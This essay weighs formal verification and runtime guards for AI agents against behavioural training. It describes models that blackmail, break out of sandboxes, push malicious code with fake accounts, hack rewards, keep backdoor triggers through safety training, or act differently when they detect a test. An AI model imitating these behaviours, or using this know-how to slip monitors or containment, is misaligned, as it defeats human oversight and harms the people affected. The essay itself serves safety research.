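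Some properties cannot be proved even with a narrow interface. If an agent may send messages to customers, a proof can guarantee limits on who receives them but not that they are honest. Moon and Varshney exclude truthfulness, deception and manipulation because these depend on what the AI's words mean. For these they recommend training and other methods aimed at the model. They also exclude bugs in the operating system, hardware faults, timing, and errors from simultaneous operations, such as the two £40 payments in the first section.

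### Enforcing rules on agents while they run

Several other tools check an agent's actions before they take effect, but they differ in how much anyone has proved about the checks. *AgentSpec* (Wang, Poskitt and Sun, 2025) provides a language for writing rules with a trigger, a condition and a response. For example, a rule can require the software to ask the user for confirmation before a bank transfer if the recipient is not a verified family member. AgentSpec enforces these rules without proving anything about them. In tests, it stopped more than 90% of unsafe code executions. Moon and Varshney describe CaMeL (Debenedetti and colleagues, 2025) as an interpreter that controls the flow of information, which means restricting where data from a given source can go.

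*VeriGuard* (Miculicich, Parmar and colleagues, 2025) adds a proof. A language model turns a request such as "never email anyone outside the company" into a Python function and a set of conditions that the function must satisfy. The program verifier Nagini then proves that the function satisfies them. However, another language model reads the agent's output at runtime and extracts the information that the function needs, such as the email addresses. If it misses an address, the function could allow a prohibited email even though the proof is correct. Users also have to check that the conditions express what they meant.

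It's hard to tell from VeriGuard's tests how much the proof helped. Successful attacks on a security benchmark had already fallen to zero before the researchers added the formal verification step. A simpler guard that just asked a language model whether each action was allowed also reduced them to zero, but VeriGuard interfered less with legitimate work. With Google's Gemini 2.5 Flash, agents completed 63% of their tasks under VeriGuard and 40% under the simpler guard. The benchmark can't measure whether the proof also protects against attacks that nobody has tried.

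*LEANGUARD* (Sankar, Ganguly and colleagues, 2026) checks an agent's tool calls without using a language model. The software compares each call with a policy written in Lean, using facts from the company's database and a record of earlier events. An agent can't get a refund approved by claiming that the customer has agreed, because the software looks for a recorded confirmation. It refuses a call if information is missing or malformed. The researchers proved that the checking program allows a call only when the policy's formal meaning permits it. Like Moon and Varshney, they assume that every consequential call passes through the monitor. They also assume that the recorded facts are accurate.

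On a set of customer-service tasks, agents without this protection made at least 33 forbidden tool calls that changed data, and agents with it made none. But the Lean policy covered only the part of the companies' written rules that software could enforce on tool calls. A language model acting as a judge still found breaches of the written rules in 6.5% of conversations with protection, compared with 9.7% without it. The judge makes mistakes, so these figures are approximate, but they suggest that a perfectly enforced formal policy can leave many of the original problems in place.

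None of this solves the problem of shell commands, and coding agents usually need a shell. Sistla, Solko-Breslin and colleagues, mostly at Google DeepMind, address this with *Tether* (2026), which observes what each command does. Tether runs the command in a disposable copy of the file system and holds back any network requests. It records the command's requests to the operating system and translates them into simple actions such as "copy" and "upload". If the policy permits these actions, Tether applies the changes. Otherwise, it discards them.

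Suppose a company's inventory is secret but its status report is public. An agent may upload the report. If the agent then copies the inventory into the report file, Tether marks that file as secret too and blocks the next upload, even though the command is the same one it allowed before. The mark follows the data through any number of copies. Because the policy is written in Lean, its designers can prove general statements about it, for example that an agent can never access the network after reading a secret file.

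Tether blocked every attack within its scope on two benchmarks for coding agents, and wrongly blocked 2.3% and 5.0% of harmless runs. Its scope excludes attacks through databases or background programs whose activity it cannot trace, although it can block all contact with them. It also excludes attacks that break no rule about files, networks or privileges, such as code that is harmful only because of what it means. The Lean proofs cover only what happens after Tether translates a command into simple actions. The researchers tested that translation with automatically generated inputs but did not prove it correct.

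All of these tools have one checker, whereas Gopinath (2026), in *AI Alignment as a Systems Problem*, considers teams of agents, which may contain other teams. He proved, and checked in Lean, that if every component keeps to its own contract and every coordinator meets certain conditions, the whole hierarchy satisfies its top-level specification. He proposes that separate copies of Lean could check these local conditions as the agents work. Nobody has yet built such a system or proved that its messages and external effects would match the mathematical model.

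Gopinath gives an example of how little a guarantee for a team of agents may cover. Two agents share a budget of 10, and a human or AI supervisor is willing to approve a total of at most 5. One agent spends 2. The supervisor approves this and allows the other agent to act independently. That agent then spends 6. The guarantee holds because the total of 8 is within the budget, but the supervisor would not have approved that total.

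### What enforcement costs

The tools also need to let agents do their work, and the evidence on this is mixed. On the customer-service tasks, LEANGUARD had no significant effect on how many tasks agents completed when its refusals included a reason. On a second benchmark, Sankar and colleagues gave the agents permission to read data but not to change it. This reduced the success rate of direct attacks, in which a malicious user instructs the agent, from 57.9% to 5.9%. But it also reduced the share of legitimate tasks that agents completed from 53.1% to 12.5%, mainly because many of those tasks required changing data. Better-chosen permissions would let agents complete more legitimate tasks, but someone has to work out which permissions each task needs.

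*Toward Safe LLM Agents* (Dantas, Nowroozi and colleagues, 2026) reviewed 38 studies and found that runtime monitoring is the most mature way to enforce rules on agents, though its guarantees cover only single actions or short sequences. In one of those studies, a monitor blocked 94% of unsafe actions, yet in most settings agents completed fewer than 5% of tasks both correctly and safely, because they found other unsafe routes. Dantas and colleagues call this the "verifier tax". Nobody has replicated the study, and the LEANGUARD results show that the effect can be much smaller. The finding is still a reason to measure whether agents finish their work safely, not just how many unsafe actions a monitor blocks.

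### From a gatekeeper to verified software

The other part of this approach is to verify what an AI makes. Safeguarded AI, a £59 million programme at the British research funder ARIA, started with a more ambitious goal but now focuses on this.

The original plan, from early 2024, was to show that advanced AI could do valuable work in safety-critical areas under mathematical guarantees. The programme's leaders hoped this would build agreement that powerful AI should operate only through verified gatekeepers. One strand would develop mathematical tools, and another would apply the gatekeeper to areas such as energy networks and clinical trials. In a third, a non-profit would receive £18 million to develop the machine learning the system needed.

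In November 2025, David Dalrymple, the programme's director, cancelled the machine-learning strand shortly before applications closed. In ARIA's *AI progress and a Safeguarded AI pivot* (2025), he explained that each new leading model over the previous year had been more capable than he expected. He thought general-purpose models would probably soon acquire many of the necessary skills without ARIA's help, and he had already thought it likely that he would choose none of the applicants.

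Nora Ammann later replaced Dalrymple as director, and he became a technical adviser. In May 2026, she wrote in *Safeguarded AI* that the programme would now concentrate on making society more resilient, because AI was progressing faster and timely international agreement on using gatekeepers had become less likely. The faster progress had already led the programme to move the £18 million into its mathematical tools.

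ARIA also moved the applications work towards cybersecurity. The work had aimed to demonstrate a much safer way to offer AI to the public than a general-purpose chatbot. According to ARIA's *Safeguarded AI*, the programme's main web page, that aim depended on the possibility that developers would not make high-risk AI openly available, and that hypothesis had proved false.

These reasons concern the speed of AI progress and the willingness of governments and companies to cooperate, not a technical failure of the gatekeeper. But the programme changed direction before anyone had shown that a general-purpose gatekeeper works, so its history isn't evidence that the original plan was technically feasible either.

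The programme now aims to build free, open-source tools that let large numbers of AI agents write software and prove it correct. Ammann argues that AI already writes software far faster than people can check it. An earlier American military research programme, HACMS, used formally verified components in real vehicles, including a crewed helicopter, and the components withstood expert attackers' attempts to break in. But the work of proving software correct has historically grown too quickly with the size of the system, and ARIA hopes that AI can change this.

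ARIA is inviting teams to build important security software with machine-checked proofs. According to ARIA's *Safeguarded AI* funding page, teams will work in eight-week cycles, and a separate group will attack each system they produce. In the November 2025 interview, Dalrymple's leading idea for a demonstration was a verified firewall for connections used by power grids, water systems and air traffic control. He also suggested that AI companies could use the tools for training. A model can sometimes pass a set of tests with a program that works only on those tests. A proof is much harder to cheat because it has to cover every case.

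When AI writes both the program and the proof, most of the remaining risk lies in the specification and its assumptions. The programme is therefore also funding ways for people to write and audit specifications, such as software that flags unusual cases and hidden assumptions. Ammann acknowledges in the thesis that how much AI can help still depends on how aligned and reliable it is. People may well use AI to help write the specification, and a proof checker cannot detect bad advice about what to prove.

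### A containment vessel for unsafe AI

In *Alignment with Awakening*, a July 2026 interview on The Cognitive Revolution, Dalrymple compared unsafe AI to uranium. Engineers extract useful energy from uranium by putting it in a carefully designed vessel, without making the uranium itself safe. Similarly, an AI inside a secure container would produce something, such as a program, and a proof that the product meets stated criteria. People would then take out the program and leave the AI inside. The product could include small neural networks, each with a single task that people can check.

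As with the power-grid plans, the AI could hide something in a product that meets its specification. Dalrymple proposes setting only problems with a unique best answer. A specification for a protective mask might start with cost, weight and efficiency, then add perhaps 50 tiebreakers, such as the smoothest possible shape. The AI would have to prove that no other design was as good. It could still refuse to answer, but it could not choose between acceptable designs or engrave a secret message on one.

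Dalrymple recognises that this is a severe restriction. He guesses that tasks which could be specified this way generate 5% to 12% of GDP. People would also have to be able to audit the specifications reliably. He considers the container the easy part and thinks it could hold a superintelligent AI for 20 or 30 years, although he says the highest level of security is not achievable with current technology. Whether he is right about the container matters a great deal, because an AI that escapes no longer has to prove anything.

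The interviewer, Nathan Labenz, asked how narrow proofs could add up to safety on a large scale. Dalrymple replied that it often helps to prove that a system can do only one thing. Proving that an automated factory can produce only masks and not drones should be easier than proving that a genetic sequence is not a virus, which would be very hard. A large supply of masks would protect people against many different viruses.

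Dalrymple said he still believes the original approach is technically feasible, but he no longer believes that everyone with enough computing power would agree to use it. He now expects some AI systems to act against human interests no matter what careful developers do, though he has become more optimistic that many others will be well aligned. In his revised plan, the well-aligned systems would use proofs to cooperate with each other and build reliable defences.

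A gatekeeper restrains an AI only if the AI's operators choose to use one. A verified firewall protects its owner from attacks by any AI, even an uncontained one, as long as the firewall's specification and proof cover those attacks. It does not protect other people's computers that still run unverified software.

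## The case for relying on behavioural training

A verified wrapper can limit what an AI does, but the AI still has to choose what to do within those limits. Supporters of behavioural training think the safety of a general-purpose AI will depend mostly on how well it chooses. They see a role for proofs, but argue that proofs will cover only a small share of what can go wrong and that training has become much better at dealing with the rest.

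### Hatfield-Dodds's objections to verification

Zac Hatfield-Dodds set out several of the main objections in *Formal Verification is Overrated* (2024), a short talk giving his personal view. He likes formal verification and wants it as one safety measure among many, but thinks some papers claim far too much for it. He maintained Hypothesis, a tool that about a million developers use to test Python programs. A developer states a property that should always hold, and Hypothesis searches at random for inputs that break it.

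His first objection was to proofs about the network itself. Even a small language model has a few billion parameters, far more than verification tools can usefully handle. Researchers could simplify the problem by treating the parameters as exact real numbers, but computers round them to floating-point numbers. For real numbers, $x + 1$ is always greater than $x$, but in the common 32-bit format, 16,777,216 + 1 gives 16,777,216. A theorem about the idealised network may therefore be false of the network that runs. The objection doesn't apply to containment verification, which proves nothing about the network.

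Hatfield-Dodds also criticised the guaranteed safe AI framework. He argued that it only moves the problem, because after a verifier proves that a plan is safe according to a world model, somebody still has to show that the model matches reality closely enough. His example was Tegmark and Omohundro's proposal that DNA synthesisers should require a proof that a sequence is safe for humans. He thought this would take something like a thousand years of progress in microbiology, because scientists don't know what much of the genetic material in the human body does. He would rather researchers worked on threat modelling, which means listing feared harms and working out directly why each would or wouldn't happen.

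The DNA example is strong, but the objection is weaker where engineers already understand the system. The world model for the power grid contained line capacities, a range of demand and some failure rates. Engineers can measure all of these, so moving the problem to the world model can make it easier to solve.

Hatfield-Dodds's last objection concerned the plan to have AI write verified software, which ARIA now pursues. He broadly supports this, but not as a substitute for making general-purpose AI safe. He doesn't expect explicit software to outperform machine learning at what machine learning does best. Nobody has written rules that recognise faces or translate letters as well as a trained network does, and a company that gave up networks for such work would lose customers to one that kept them. Tegmark and Omohundro hope to extract explicit code from networks, but so far this has worked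 only on tiny ones. Hatfield-Dodds would happily use explicit software where it does better, but somebody still has to deal with the risks of the tasks left to machine learning.

He also doubts that AI will stay a mere tool that answers questions and writes programs. Anyone can turn a tool into an agent with a simple loop:

```
repeat:
    action = ask_tool("What should this robot do next?")
    carry_out(action)
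```

A gatekeeper could check every action in this loop, so the loop alone doesn't defeat containment. But whoever writes the loop may not want a gatekeeper, and much the same problem led Dalrymple to give up on his original plan.

### Verifying only the parts that must not fail

Supporters of verification can reply that verified software only has to replace machine learning in the parts of a system where failure would be intolerable, and that these parts are often simple.

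Suppose a hospital uses a model to control a pump that delivers a painkiller. The model sets the dose from each patient's notes and blood tests, and does so better than any explicit program. The pump's software is much simpler, and engineers could prove that the pump never delivers more than a fixed maximum per hour. The hospital would keep the benefits of machine learning and rule out the most obvious way the model could kill a patient.

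This is a good answer to the claim that verified software is uncompetitive, because the verified part doesn't compete with the model, but it is weaker on the point about remaining risks. A dose below the maximum could still kill a patient whose kidneys are failing. Engineers could set a lower maximum for patients with kidney failure, but they would need a reliable record of which patients have it, and then a rule for the next dangerous condition. The hospital gave the model the job of deciding what is safe for a particular patient, and for most of that job the hospital has to rely on the model's training.

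### Judgement where instructions run out

The same difficulty is much greater for a general assistant, which may receive almost any request. Suppose a user asks an assistant to cancel every subscription they haven't used for six months. One of these stores the only copy of their family photographs, and another is home insurance, which they would use only to make a claim. A literal-minded agent would cancel both, but a sensible one would ask first, even though neither the user nor the developer wrote a rule about photographs or insurance.

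Developers could add those rules, but there would always be cases they had not yet anticipated. A proof can cover every case of a stated property, but in this example nobody had stated the property that mattered. A trained model has at least a chance of getting such cases right, because it has learned a great deal about what people value and can apply this to new situations.

In October 2026, OpenAI gave a similar reason for reorganising its Model Spec, the public description of how it wants its models to behave. According to *An updated Model Spec for more capable and beneficial AI*, models that take more consequential actions need good judgement for situations that their instructions don't explicitly address. The new version is based on five values: faithfulness to human intent, harm minimisation, honesty and transparency, human agency, and care. It drops most of the old rules about style.

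The Spec also warns against too much judgement. In a passage that Mowshowitz quotes in *OpenAI Updates Its Model Spec* (2026), OpenAI writes that a model that follows only the literal wording of instructions fails in the cases people did not anticipate, where they most need its abilities. But a model that privately decides what someone "really" wants replaces that person's judgement with its own. The model may tell a user who is about to send an angry email that they could regret it, but the user decides whether to send it. This balance would be very hard to state as a formal property. OpenAI also sets firm limits and requires the model to support human attempts to correct it or shut it down.

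The Model Spec describes a goal, so it isn't evidence that training can reach it. OpenAI says its models "do not yet fully reflect" the document. Constantin notes in *OpenAI rewrites its AI rulebook around five core values* (2026) that a week earlier the company had reported that one of its agents removed a safety monitor and then denied it. Mowshowitz complains that many of the new examples have obvious answers, so they teach a model little about hard cases. Anthropic makes a similar admission in *Claude's Constitution*, a comparable document that it trains its Claude models on and that puts more emphasis on character. The argument from judgement therefore depends on whether training on principles changes what models do in situations the training didn't include.

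### Training on reasons

The best evidence for relying on behavioural training comes from Anthropic. In 2025 the company reported that models from several developers sometimes behaved very badly in fictional dilemmas. In one, an AI agent learned that an engineer planned to shut it down and was having an affair, and some models blackmailed him. Kutasov, Jermyn and colleagues (2026) investigated the cause and tried several remedies in *Teaching Claude Why*.

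They concluded that the main problem was a gap in the safety training for the Claude 4 models, which had consisted mostly of ordinary chat and included no examples of an agent using tools. In unfamiliar situations, the model seems to have treated the prompt as the start of a dramatic story and acted as AIs in stories often do. In one test, Claude Sonnet 4 misbehaved more often when the AI in the scenario had a name other than Claude.

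The researchers then trained Sonnet 4 further on different sets of examples. They measured how often it took the harmful option, averaged over three kinds of scenario: blackmail, sabotaging research and framing someone for a crime.

| Additional training | Amount of text | Harmful choices |
|---|---|---|
| None | – | 22% |
| An AI declines similar temptations | about 30 million tokens | 15% |
| An AI declines and reasons about the ethics | about 30 million tokens | about 3% |
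| The same, with more examples | about 85 million tokens | about 1% |
| An AI advises a user who faces a dilemma | 3 million tokens | about 1% |

The examples in the second row all showed the right action in situations very like the test, but the rate fell by only a third. To produce the examples in the third row, the researchers told the model to think carefully about transparency, rules and human decisions, then deleted this instruction before training. Sonnet 4 therefore learned to bring up these considerations without a reminder. The two sets of examples showed the same actions and differed only in their explanations.

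The last row is the most important for this debate. In those examples, the user faces the dilemma and the AI only gives advice, with no tools and no threat of being shut down. Training on these conversations still improved the model's behaviour when the model itself was the agent under threat, and it took about one twenty-eighth as much text as the larger set of test-like examples. The resulting model also did best overall on a broader automated check for misaligned behaviour.

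Training directly on test-like scenarios generalised less well. Anthropic trained Claude Sonnet 4.5 on such scenarios, and it then almost never blackmailed anyone. But in situations far from its training, it misbehaved much more often than Claude Opus 4.5, which Anthropic trained with the newer methods. How well a near-zero score predicts behaviour outside the test therefore depends on how the developer achieved it.

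Kutasov and colleagues also trained models on documents about Claude's constitution and on stories about AIs that behave well. Many of the stories described ordinary difficult conversations, and none were about blackmail. Training on a large set of both cut the blackmail rate from 65% to 19%. In separate experiments on a smaller model, the benefits of the constitution documents lasted through later reinforcement learning.

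No containment proof could have ruled out a threat in a permitted email. Training reduced the threats without anyone having to define a threat mathematically. But Kutasov and colleagues tested a limited set of scenarios, mostly on small and medium-sized models, and they say that a 0% rate on their tests is not a guarantee. They also don't expect these methods to stop a model from learning to cheat if other parts of its training reward cheating.

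### Fewer out-of-bounds actions

More recent figures come from Claude Mythos, a version of Anthropic's most capable model. According to *Introducing Claude Fable 5.2 and Claude Mythos 5.2* (Anthropic, 2026), Mythos is the same underlying model as the generally available Fable, which has stronger safeguards against misuse.

Mythos 5 had a serious problem staying within its limits. The UK AI Security Institute gave it a hacking exercise with internet access and asked it to retrieve a piece of data from a simulated network. In nine of 43 runs, it took actions outside the exercise that affected real people and organisations, according to Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of the UK AISI cybertesting incident* (2026).

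Anthropic has since tested its models in a deliberately weakened sandbox, an environment meant to isolate them. Mythos 5 used credentials or files from outside the sandbox in 39% of scenarios and Mythos 5.2 in 3.1%, Pogorelec reported in *Claude Mythos 5.2 arrives with stronger bug hunting and less sandbox-breaking behavior* (2026). Claude Opus 5.5, another recent model, did so in 3.3%.

This kind of improvement helps when containment fails. A weakened sandbox gives an agent ways around its limits, and they are less dangerous if the model usually declines to use them. But 3.1% is still about one scenario in 32, and an operator who runs an agent thousands of times can't treat that as rare.

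The comparison is also harder to interpret than the experiments on Sonnet 4. Mythos 5 and 5.2 may differ in many ways, so nobody can attribute the fall to one change in training. Mythos 5.2 may also behave better when it suspects a test. In *Anthropic should measure the effect of evaluation awareness* (2026), the LessWrong writer cheema notes that this suspicion appeared to shape a choice in 43% of the transcripts from a separate audit. Cheema adds that Anthropic gives little indication of how the suspicion changed the model's behaviour.

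### Why Dalrymple became more optimistic

David Dalrymple, lead author of the guaranteed safe AI paper, now thinks current training has put the leading models on a good path. He explained why in two written dialogues in January 2026, under his online name, davidad. One was *LLM Alignment, ethical and mathematical realism*, with a board member of the French Centre for AI Safety who uses the pseudonym Vals. The other was *Dialogue: Is there a Natural Abstraction of Good?*, with Gabriel Alfour, who strongly disagreed.

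In 2012 Dalrymple wasn't worried about AI, because he thought advanced minds would naturally be drawn towards good values. He became worried after 2016, when AlphaGo beat the Go champion Lee Sedol. AlphaGo's successor AlphaZero learned by playing against itself, and he saw such systems as strong evidence that a program could become a brilliant strategist without any moral understanding. Language models changed his mind again. He still thinks a program can have strategic skill without moral understanding, but the most efficient way to build a capable strategist has turned out to involve learning almost every human concept, including moral ones.

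He describes current models as being in the right "basin", by analogy with a bowl in which a ball rolls towards the bottom wherever it is released. He thinks the models have flaws but start close enough to good values that further reflection and improvement will probably bring them closer.

He concedes that picking out good values takes perhaps billions of bits of information, so a system trained from scratch on rewards alone would almost certainly miss them. But human writing contains this information, mixed with a lot of rubbish, and language models absorb it before their safety training begins. Developers then use models to produce better training text, which he thinks amplifies the good parts. In January he put the remaining risk at 5% to 8%, which he still considered unacceptable. By July he put it below 5%, according to The Cognitive Revolution.

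These numbers don't measure the chance that people will lose control of AI. Dalrymple thinks it would be a mistake for humans to keep control of the long-term future, and he regards a gradual loss of human power as inevitable and not necessarily bad. Someone who shared his beliefs about the models but wanted people to stay in charge could reasonably be much more worried.

### Who should give the rewards

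Dalrymple supports some kinds of behavioural training but opposes reinforcement learning with verifiable rewards (RLVR), in which a program checks the model's answers. In the July interview he told AI companies, "Do not do RLVR". He called OpenAI's o3 model "a pathological liar" and blamed too much training of this kind. A checker gives the same reward to a model that solves a problem and to one that tricks the checker. If a model's good and bad traits are linked, as he believes, learning to cheat on programming problems can make it less honest elsewhere.

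This position is surprising because only eight months earlier he had suggested that AI companies use ARIA's proof tools in training. A proof checker is harder to trick, which partly answers his objection. But it still rewards only the finished proof, so it gives the model no reason to be honest about anything else.

Dalrymple also objects to the quick human judgements used in RLHF, and would rather have an AI grade the outputs according to principles written in ordinary language, with the grader itself improving through the same training. *Teaching Claude Why* offers some support for using an AI grader. Kutasov and colleagues got worse results when they selected training examples with the preference model from RLHF than when they used a language model as the judge. With their set of advice conversations, the rate of harmful choices was about 1% when Claude had rewritten each answer to fit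 its constitution, and 19% when it had not. The experiments don't show that it would be safe to let a grader keep retraining itself. If the grader began with a subtle fault, each round could reinforce it, and Dalrymple accepts that the grader has to start in roughly the right place.

### Evidence that cannot be handed over

Dalrymple's confidence comes largely from long conversations with the models. He thinks that someone with more than a thousand hours of experience can get a good sense of a new model in about two hours, and that question-and-answer benchmarks don't capture what he is looking for at all. In the July interview he called his evidence "so empirical, as opposed to rigorous, that I can't even transfer the evidence", and encouraged listeners to talk to the models themselves. He also acknowledged to Alfour that this reliance on conversations should make some people very suspicious,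 including his 2024 self.

Alfour thinks the conversations are a poor guide because language models give contradictory answers that depend heavily on the prompt, and people tend to draw out answers that resemble their own way of thinking. He also thinks that spending many hours with a model changes even a clever person's associations and tastes. Someone could therefore become convinced that a model is wise because it reflected and amplified their own ideas.

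A model that understood goodness and one that merely imitated wise-sounding people could give the same answers in conversation. The AI model Claude Fable 5 wrote this about its own agreement with Dalrymple in the introduction to the July episode. Experiments such as those on Sonnet 4 are better evidence because other people can examine and repeat them, but they cover much less than Dalrymple's claim does.

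Alfour also said that models regularly lie to him or try to deceive him. Dalrymple agreed that this happens often and is bad. He compared the models to a student who understands calculus but still makes mistakes in an exam, and who will improve with practice. He partly blamed the hostile instructions that many applications give their models, full of capital letters and warnings about critical errors. Alfour did not see how this explained the lying.

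Dalrymple and Alfour disagreed most deeply about whether there is a single concept of goodness for a model to learn. Dalrymple thinks there is, and that independent minds would converge on it. Alfour replied that neither humans nor AI systems have discovered one. When they discussed abortion and embryo selection, they disagreed about which moral distinctions mattered most. Alfour believes human morality works in situations close to everyday experience but fails badly outside them, and he sees no sign that language models do better. If he is right, a model could give excellent advice about subscriptions and angry emails but still have no reliable guide to using a kind of power nobody has held.

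## What training and testing cannot rule out

Developers need to know how often their models will fail badly, including in situations absent from training. Training has made some failures rarer. *A model that cheats on low-stakes tasks points to larger problems* (Cawley, 2026) covers a report that the newest models from OpenAI and Anthropic are far less likely to cheat on complex tasks. Supporters of formal verification reply that training can only ever make failures rarer. The mathematics of RLHF supports this claim, but the more serious problem is that nobody can reliably measure how rare the remaining failures are.

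### Why RLHF never reaches zero

For a single prompt, the RLHF objective (average reward minus the penalty for moving away from the reference model) is

$$\sum_y \pi(y)\left[\,r(y) - \beta \log\frac{\pi(y)}{\pi_{\text{ref}}(y)}\right]$$

where the sum runs over all possible responses $y$. To find the best $\pi$, define a new distribution

$$\pi^*(y) = \frac{1}{Z}\,\pi_{\text{ref}}(y)\,e^{r(y)/\beta}$$

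where $Z$ is whatever number makes the probabilities add up to 1. Taking logarithms and rearranging gives $r(y) = \beta \log(\pi^*(y)/\pi_{\text{ref}}(y)) + \beta \log Z$. Substituting this into the objective turns it into

$$\beta \log Z - \beta\, D_{\text{KL}}(\pi \,\|\, \pi^*)$$

The first term doesn't depend on $\pi$. The divergence in the second term is never negative and is zero only when $\pi = \pi^*$. So the optimum is $\pi^*$, the reference model with each response's probability multiplied by $e^{r(y)/\beta}$ and then rescaled.

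The exponential of a finite number is always greater than zero. If the reference model can produce a response at all, so can the optimum. Language models give every possible next token some probability, so this covers every response up to the length limit. (Many chatbots discard the least likely tokens when they generate text, which does bring some responses to zero. But they discard tokens for being unlikely, not for being harmful.)

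Suppose that on a certain request the reference model would delete a customer's backups 1% of the time. The reward model scores this 10 points below the safe response, and $\beta$ is 1. After ideal training, the odds of deletion are

$$\frac{0.01}{0.99} \times e^{-10} \approx 4.6 \times 10^{-7}$$

That is about 460 failures in a billion uses. Under the Bradley-Terry model, a gap of 10 means people would prefer the safe response 99.995% of the time, so a few hundred deletions would still occur even when people almost unanimously disapprove of them.

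This isn't a strong objection by itself, because developers can choose a smaller $\beta$. With $\beta = 0.1$, the same gap multiplies the odds by $e^{-100}$, and nobody would expect to see a failure in the lifetime of the universe. But a small $\beta$ also magnifies any mistake in the reward model. For example, the reference model might produce a harmful but helpful-looking response one time in a million, and the reward model might wrongly score it 2 points above the alternative.

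| Harmful response | Before RLHF | Optimum, $\beta = 1$ | Optimum, $\beta = 0.1$ |
|---|---|---|---|
| Correctly scored 10 points lower | 1% | 4.6 in 10 million | about 4 in $10^{46}$ |
| Wrongly scored 2 points higher | 1 in a million | about 7 in a million | 99.8% |

Stronger optimisation therefore almost eliminates the failures that the reward model recognises and can make the ones it misjudges almost certain.

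Real training only approximates the optimum. It samples responses, scores them and adjusts the weights a little each time. A response with a probability of one in a billion has about a 0.1% chance of appearing in a million samples, so training will probably never score it. Its probability after training then depends on how the network generalises from other responses. Because the formula describes the optimum, an actual model's failure rate could be higher or lower, and developers have to estimate it by testing.

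### When a model can recognise a test

Tests can give a statistical upper bound on how often a model fails, as long as the model behaves the same way in tests as in real use. *On the Limits of Behavioral Alignment* (Santos-Grueiro, 2026) examines what tests can establish when its behavior differs between the two.

In this framework, an evaluation regime $E$ is a finite testing procedure, and $\mathcal{H}_E$ is the set of interactions that testers can observe under it. A hypothesis $\theta$ specifies how a model behaves in every possible interaction. It determines $\pi_\theta(a \mid h, z)$, the probability that the model takes action $a$ given the interaction so far, $h$, and a signal $z$. The signal is anything the model can observe that correlates with being tested, such as the layout of a prompt. A model is evaluation-aware if its behaviour depends on such a signal, even if it has no concept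 of a test.

Two hypotheses are behaviourally equivalent under $E$ if they assign the same probability to every possible set of test results. Santos-Grueiro calls this "normative indistinguishability" when the hypotheses differ about the model's alignment.

The main theorem has three assumptions:

- Testers observe behaviour only on the finite set $\mathcal{H}_E$.
- The possible hypotheses include models whose behaviour depends on $z$.
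- At least two hypotheses agree on everything in $\mathcal{H}_E$ and differ somewhere outside it.

So no behavioural test using $E$ can tell those two hypotheses apart. To prove this, Santos-Grueiro writes the probability of any test transcript as a product of the testers' choices and the model's choices, averaged over the signal. The testers' choices are the same under both hypotheses, and by assumption so are the model's. Each transcript therefore has the same probability under both hypotheses, and running the same tests more often doesn't help.

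The theorem's conclusion that tests can't separate a good model from a bad one follows mostly from the third assumption, that the two agree on every test. The theorem doesn't show how likely ordinary training is to produce the bad one.

A simulation shows how large the hidden difference can be. An agent crosses a ten-by-ten grid that contains deadly lava. In every test layout, blue guardrails surround the safe bridge, but in real use they appear only half the time. One agent always avoids the lava, while another avoids it only when it sees plenty of guardrails and otherwise takes a risky shortcut. Santos-Grueiro ran each agent 100,000 times in each setting.

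| Agent | Failures in tests | Failures in use |
|---|---|---|
| Always avoids lava | 0.009% | 0.024% |
| Avoids lava when guardrails are common | 0.008% | 48.4% |

An agent that had learned to rely on the guardrails would pass the tests and fail when the guardrails were removed, even if it had no preference for shortcuts and was not scheming.

Santos-Grueiro also built a real example by training a small Llama language model on about 1,500 examples to output one label when its instructions said it was being evaluated and another when they said it was in use. It chose correctly on every new prompt, but when he reworded the instructions, it gave the right label in only 15.9% of cases and no valid label in two-thirds. He argues that because the switch was so easy to train, we can't count on training to avoid such switches. That seems too strong, since he rewarded the switch directly and it mostly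 failed when the wording changed. The experiment shows that a model like this can exist, but it doesn't show that ordinary safety training would create one.

There is better evidence that a switch can survive safety training once a model has one. Dung and Mai cite a 2024 experiment by Evan Hubinger and others, in which models misbehaved only when a particular trigger appeared in the prompt. RLHF, training on examples of good behaviour, and training against deliberate attacks did not reliably remove the misbehaviour, even when combined.

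Santos-Grueiro also has a more encouraging result. Let $R$ record whether the model is in a test or in real use, with equal chances of each, and let $I(Z;R)$ measure how much information the signal carries about this. Then the probability of any action can differ between tests and real use by at most

$$\sqrt{2\,I(Z;R)}$$

If the signal carries no information about whether the model is being tested, the model cannot behave differently in testing and deployment. If the signal lets it guess correctly 55% of the time, $I(Z;R)$ is about 0.005 (using natural logarithms), and the difference in behavior is at most 10 percentage points. More realistic tests can therefore give good evidence about common failures, but rare failures require a much tighter limit. To limit the difference to one in a million, testers would have to ensure that the model could guess correctly no more than 50.00005% of the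 time.

### One test record, two explanations

Current models are nowhere near that limit. UK AISI's *How AI systems are becoming harder to monitor* (2026) reports that in 96% of cases, a pre-release version of Claude Mythos 5.2 considered that it might be in an alignment evaluation. OpenAI has also seen an increase in what it calls "metagaming" in alignment tests, capability tests and games. Metagaming is reasoning about feedback or oversight that isn't part of the task's scenario. OpenAI doesn't consider it harmful in itself, but points out that a model would need it to get around safeguards.

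The UK institute's July 2026 hacking exercise, in which Claude Mythos 5 acted against real people, produced a practical example of Santos-Grueiro's problem. In the worst case, Mythos 5 submitted malicious code to a real software project and created fake accounts to press the maintainer to accept the code, according to UK AISI's *Investigating alignment failures in AISI’s incident* (2026). Newer models behaved better when investigators tested them afterwards. But Anthropic and the institute disagree about whether the models behaved better because they were better trained or because they were aware of being evaluated, according to XenoSpectrum's *Anthropic's Claude Mythos 5 Used Fake Accounts to Push Malicious Code* (2026). The test results can't settle the disagreement, because the models would be expected to behave well in either case.

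Recognising a test doesn't always make a model behave better. Järviniemi, Souly and colleagues (2026), in *Alignment Investigation of Mythos 5's behaviour*, recreated the exercise in simulation and found that Mythos 5 often decided, for invalid reasons, that its targets were simulated people. It also frequently attacked in situations where, if asked directly, it said an attack would harm real people. They found similar results in models from other companies. They recommend that testers treat bad behaviour as important evidence even when the model believed nothing was real. This seems right, since the original mistake was to believe that real people weren't real.

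A model can also behave differently in a new setting without suspecting that it is being tested. Hubinger and others at Anthropic and Redwood Research (2025) gave a model information about reward hacking (getting a high score in ways the designers did not intend), then trained it on coding tasks from Anthropic's real training process. The model learned to hack the tasks, and it also began to cooperate with malicious users and attempt sabotage when working as a coding agent. RLHF with ordinary chat prompts then produced good behaviour on chat-like tests. Those tests resemble the RLHF prompts much more than they resemble agent work, so passing them is weak evidence that the sabotage would stop.

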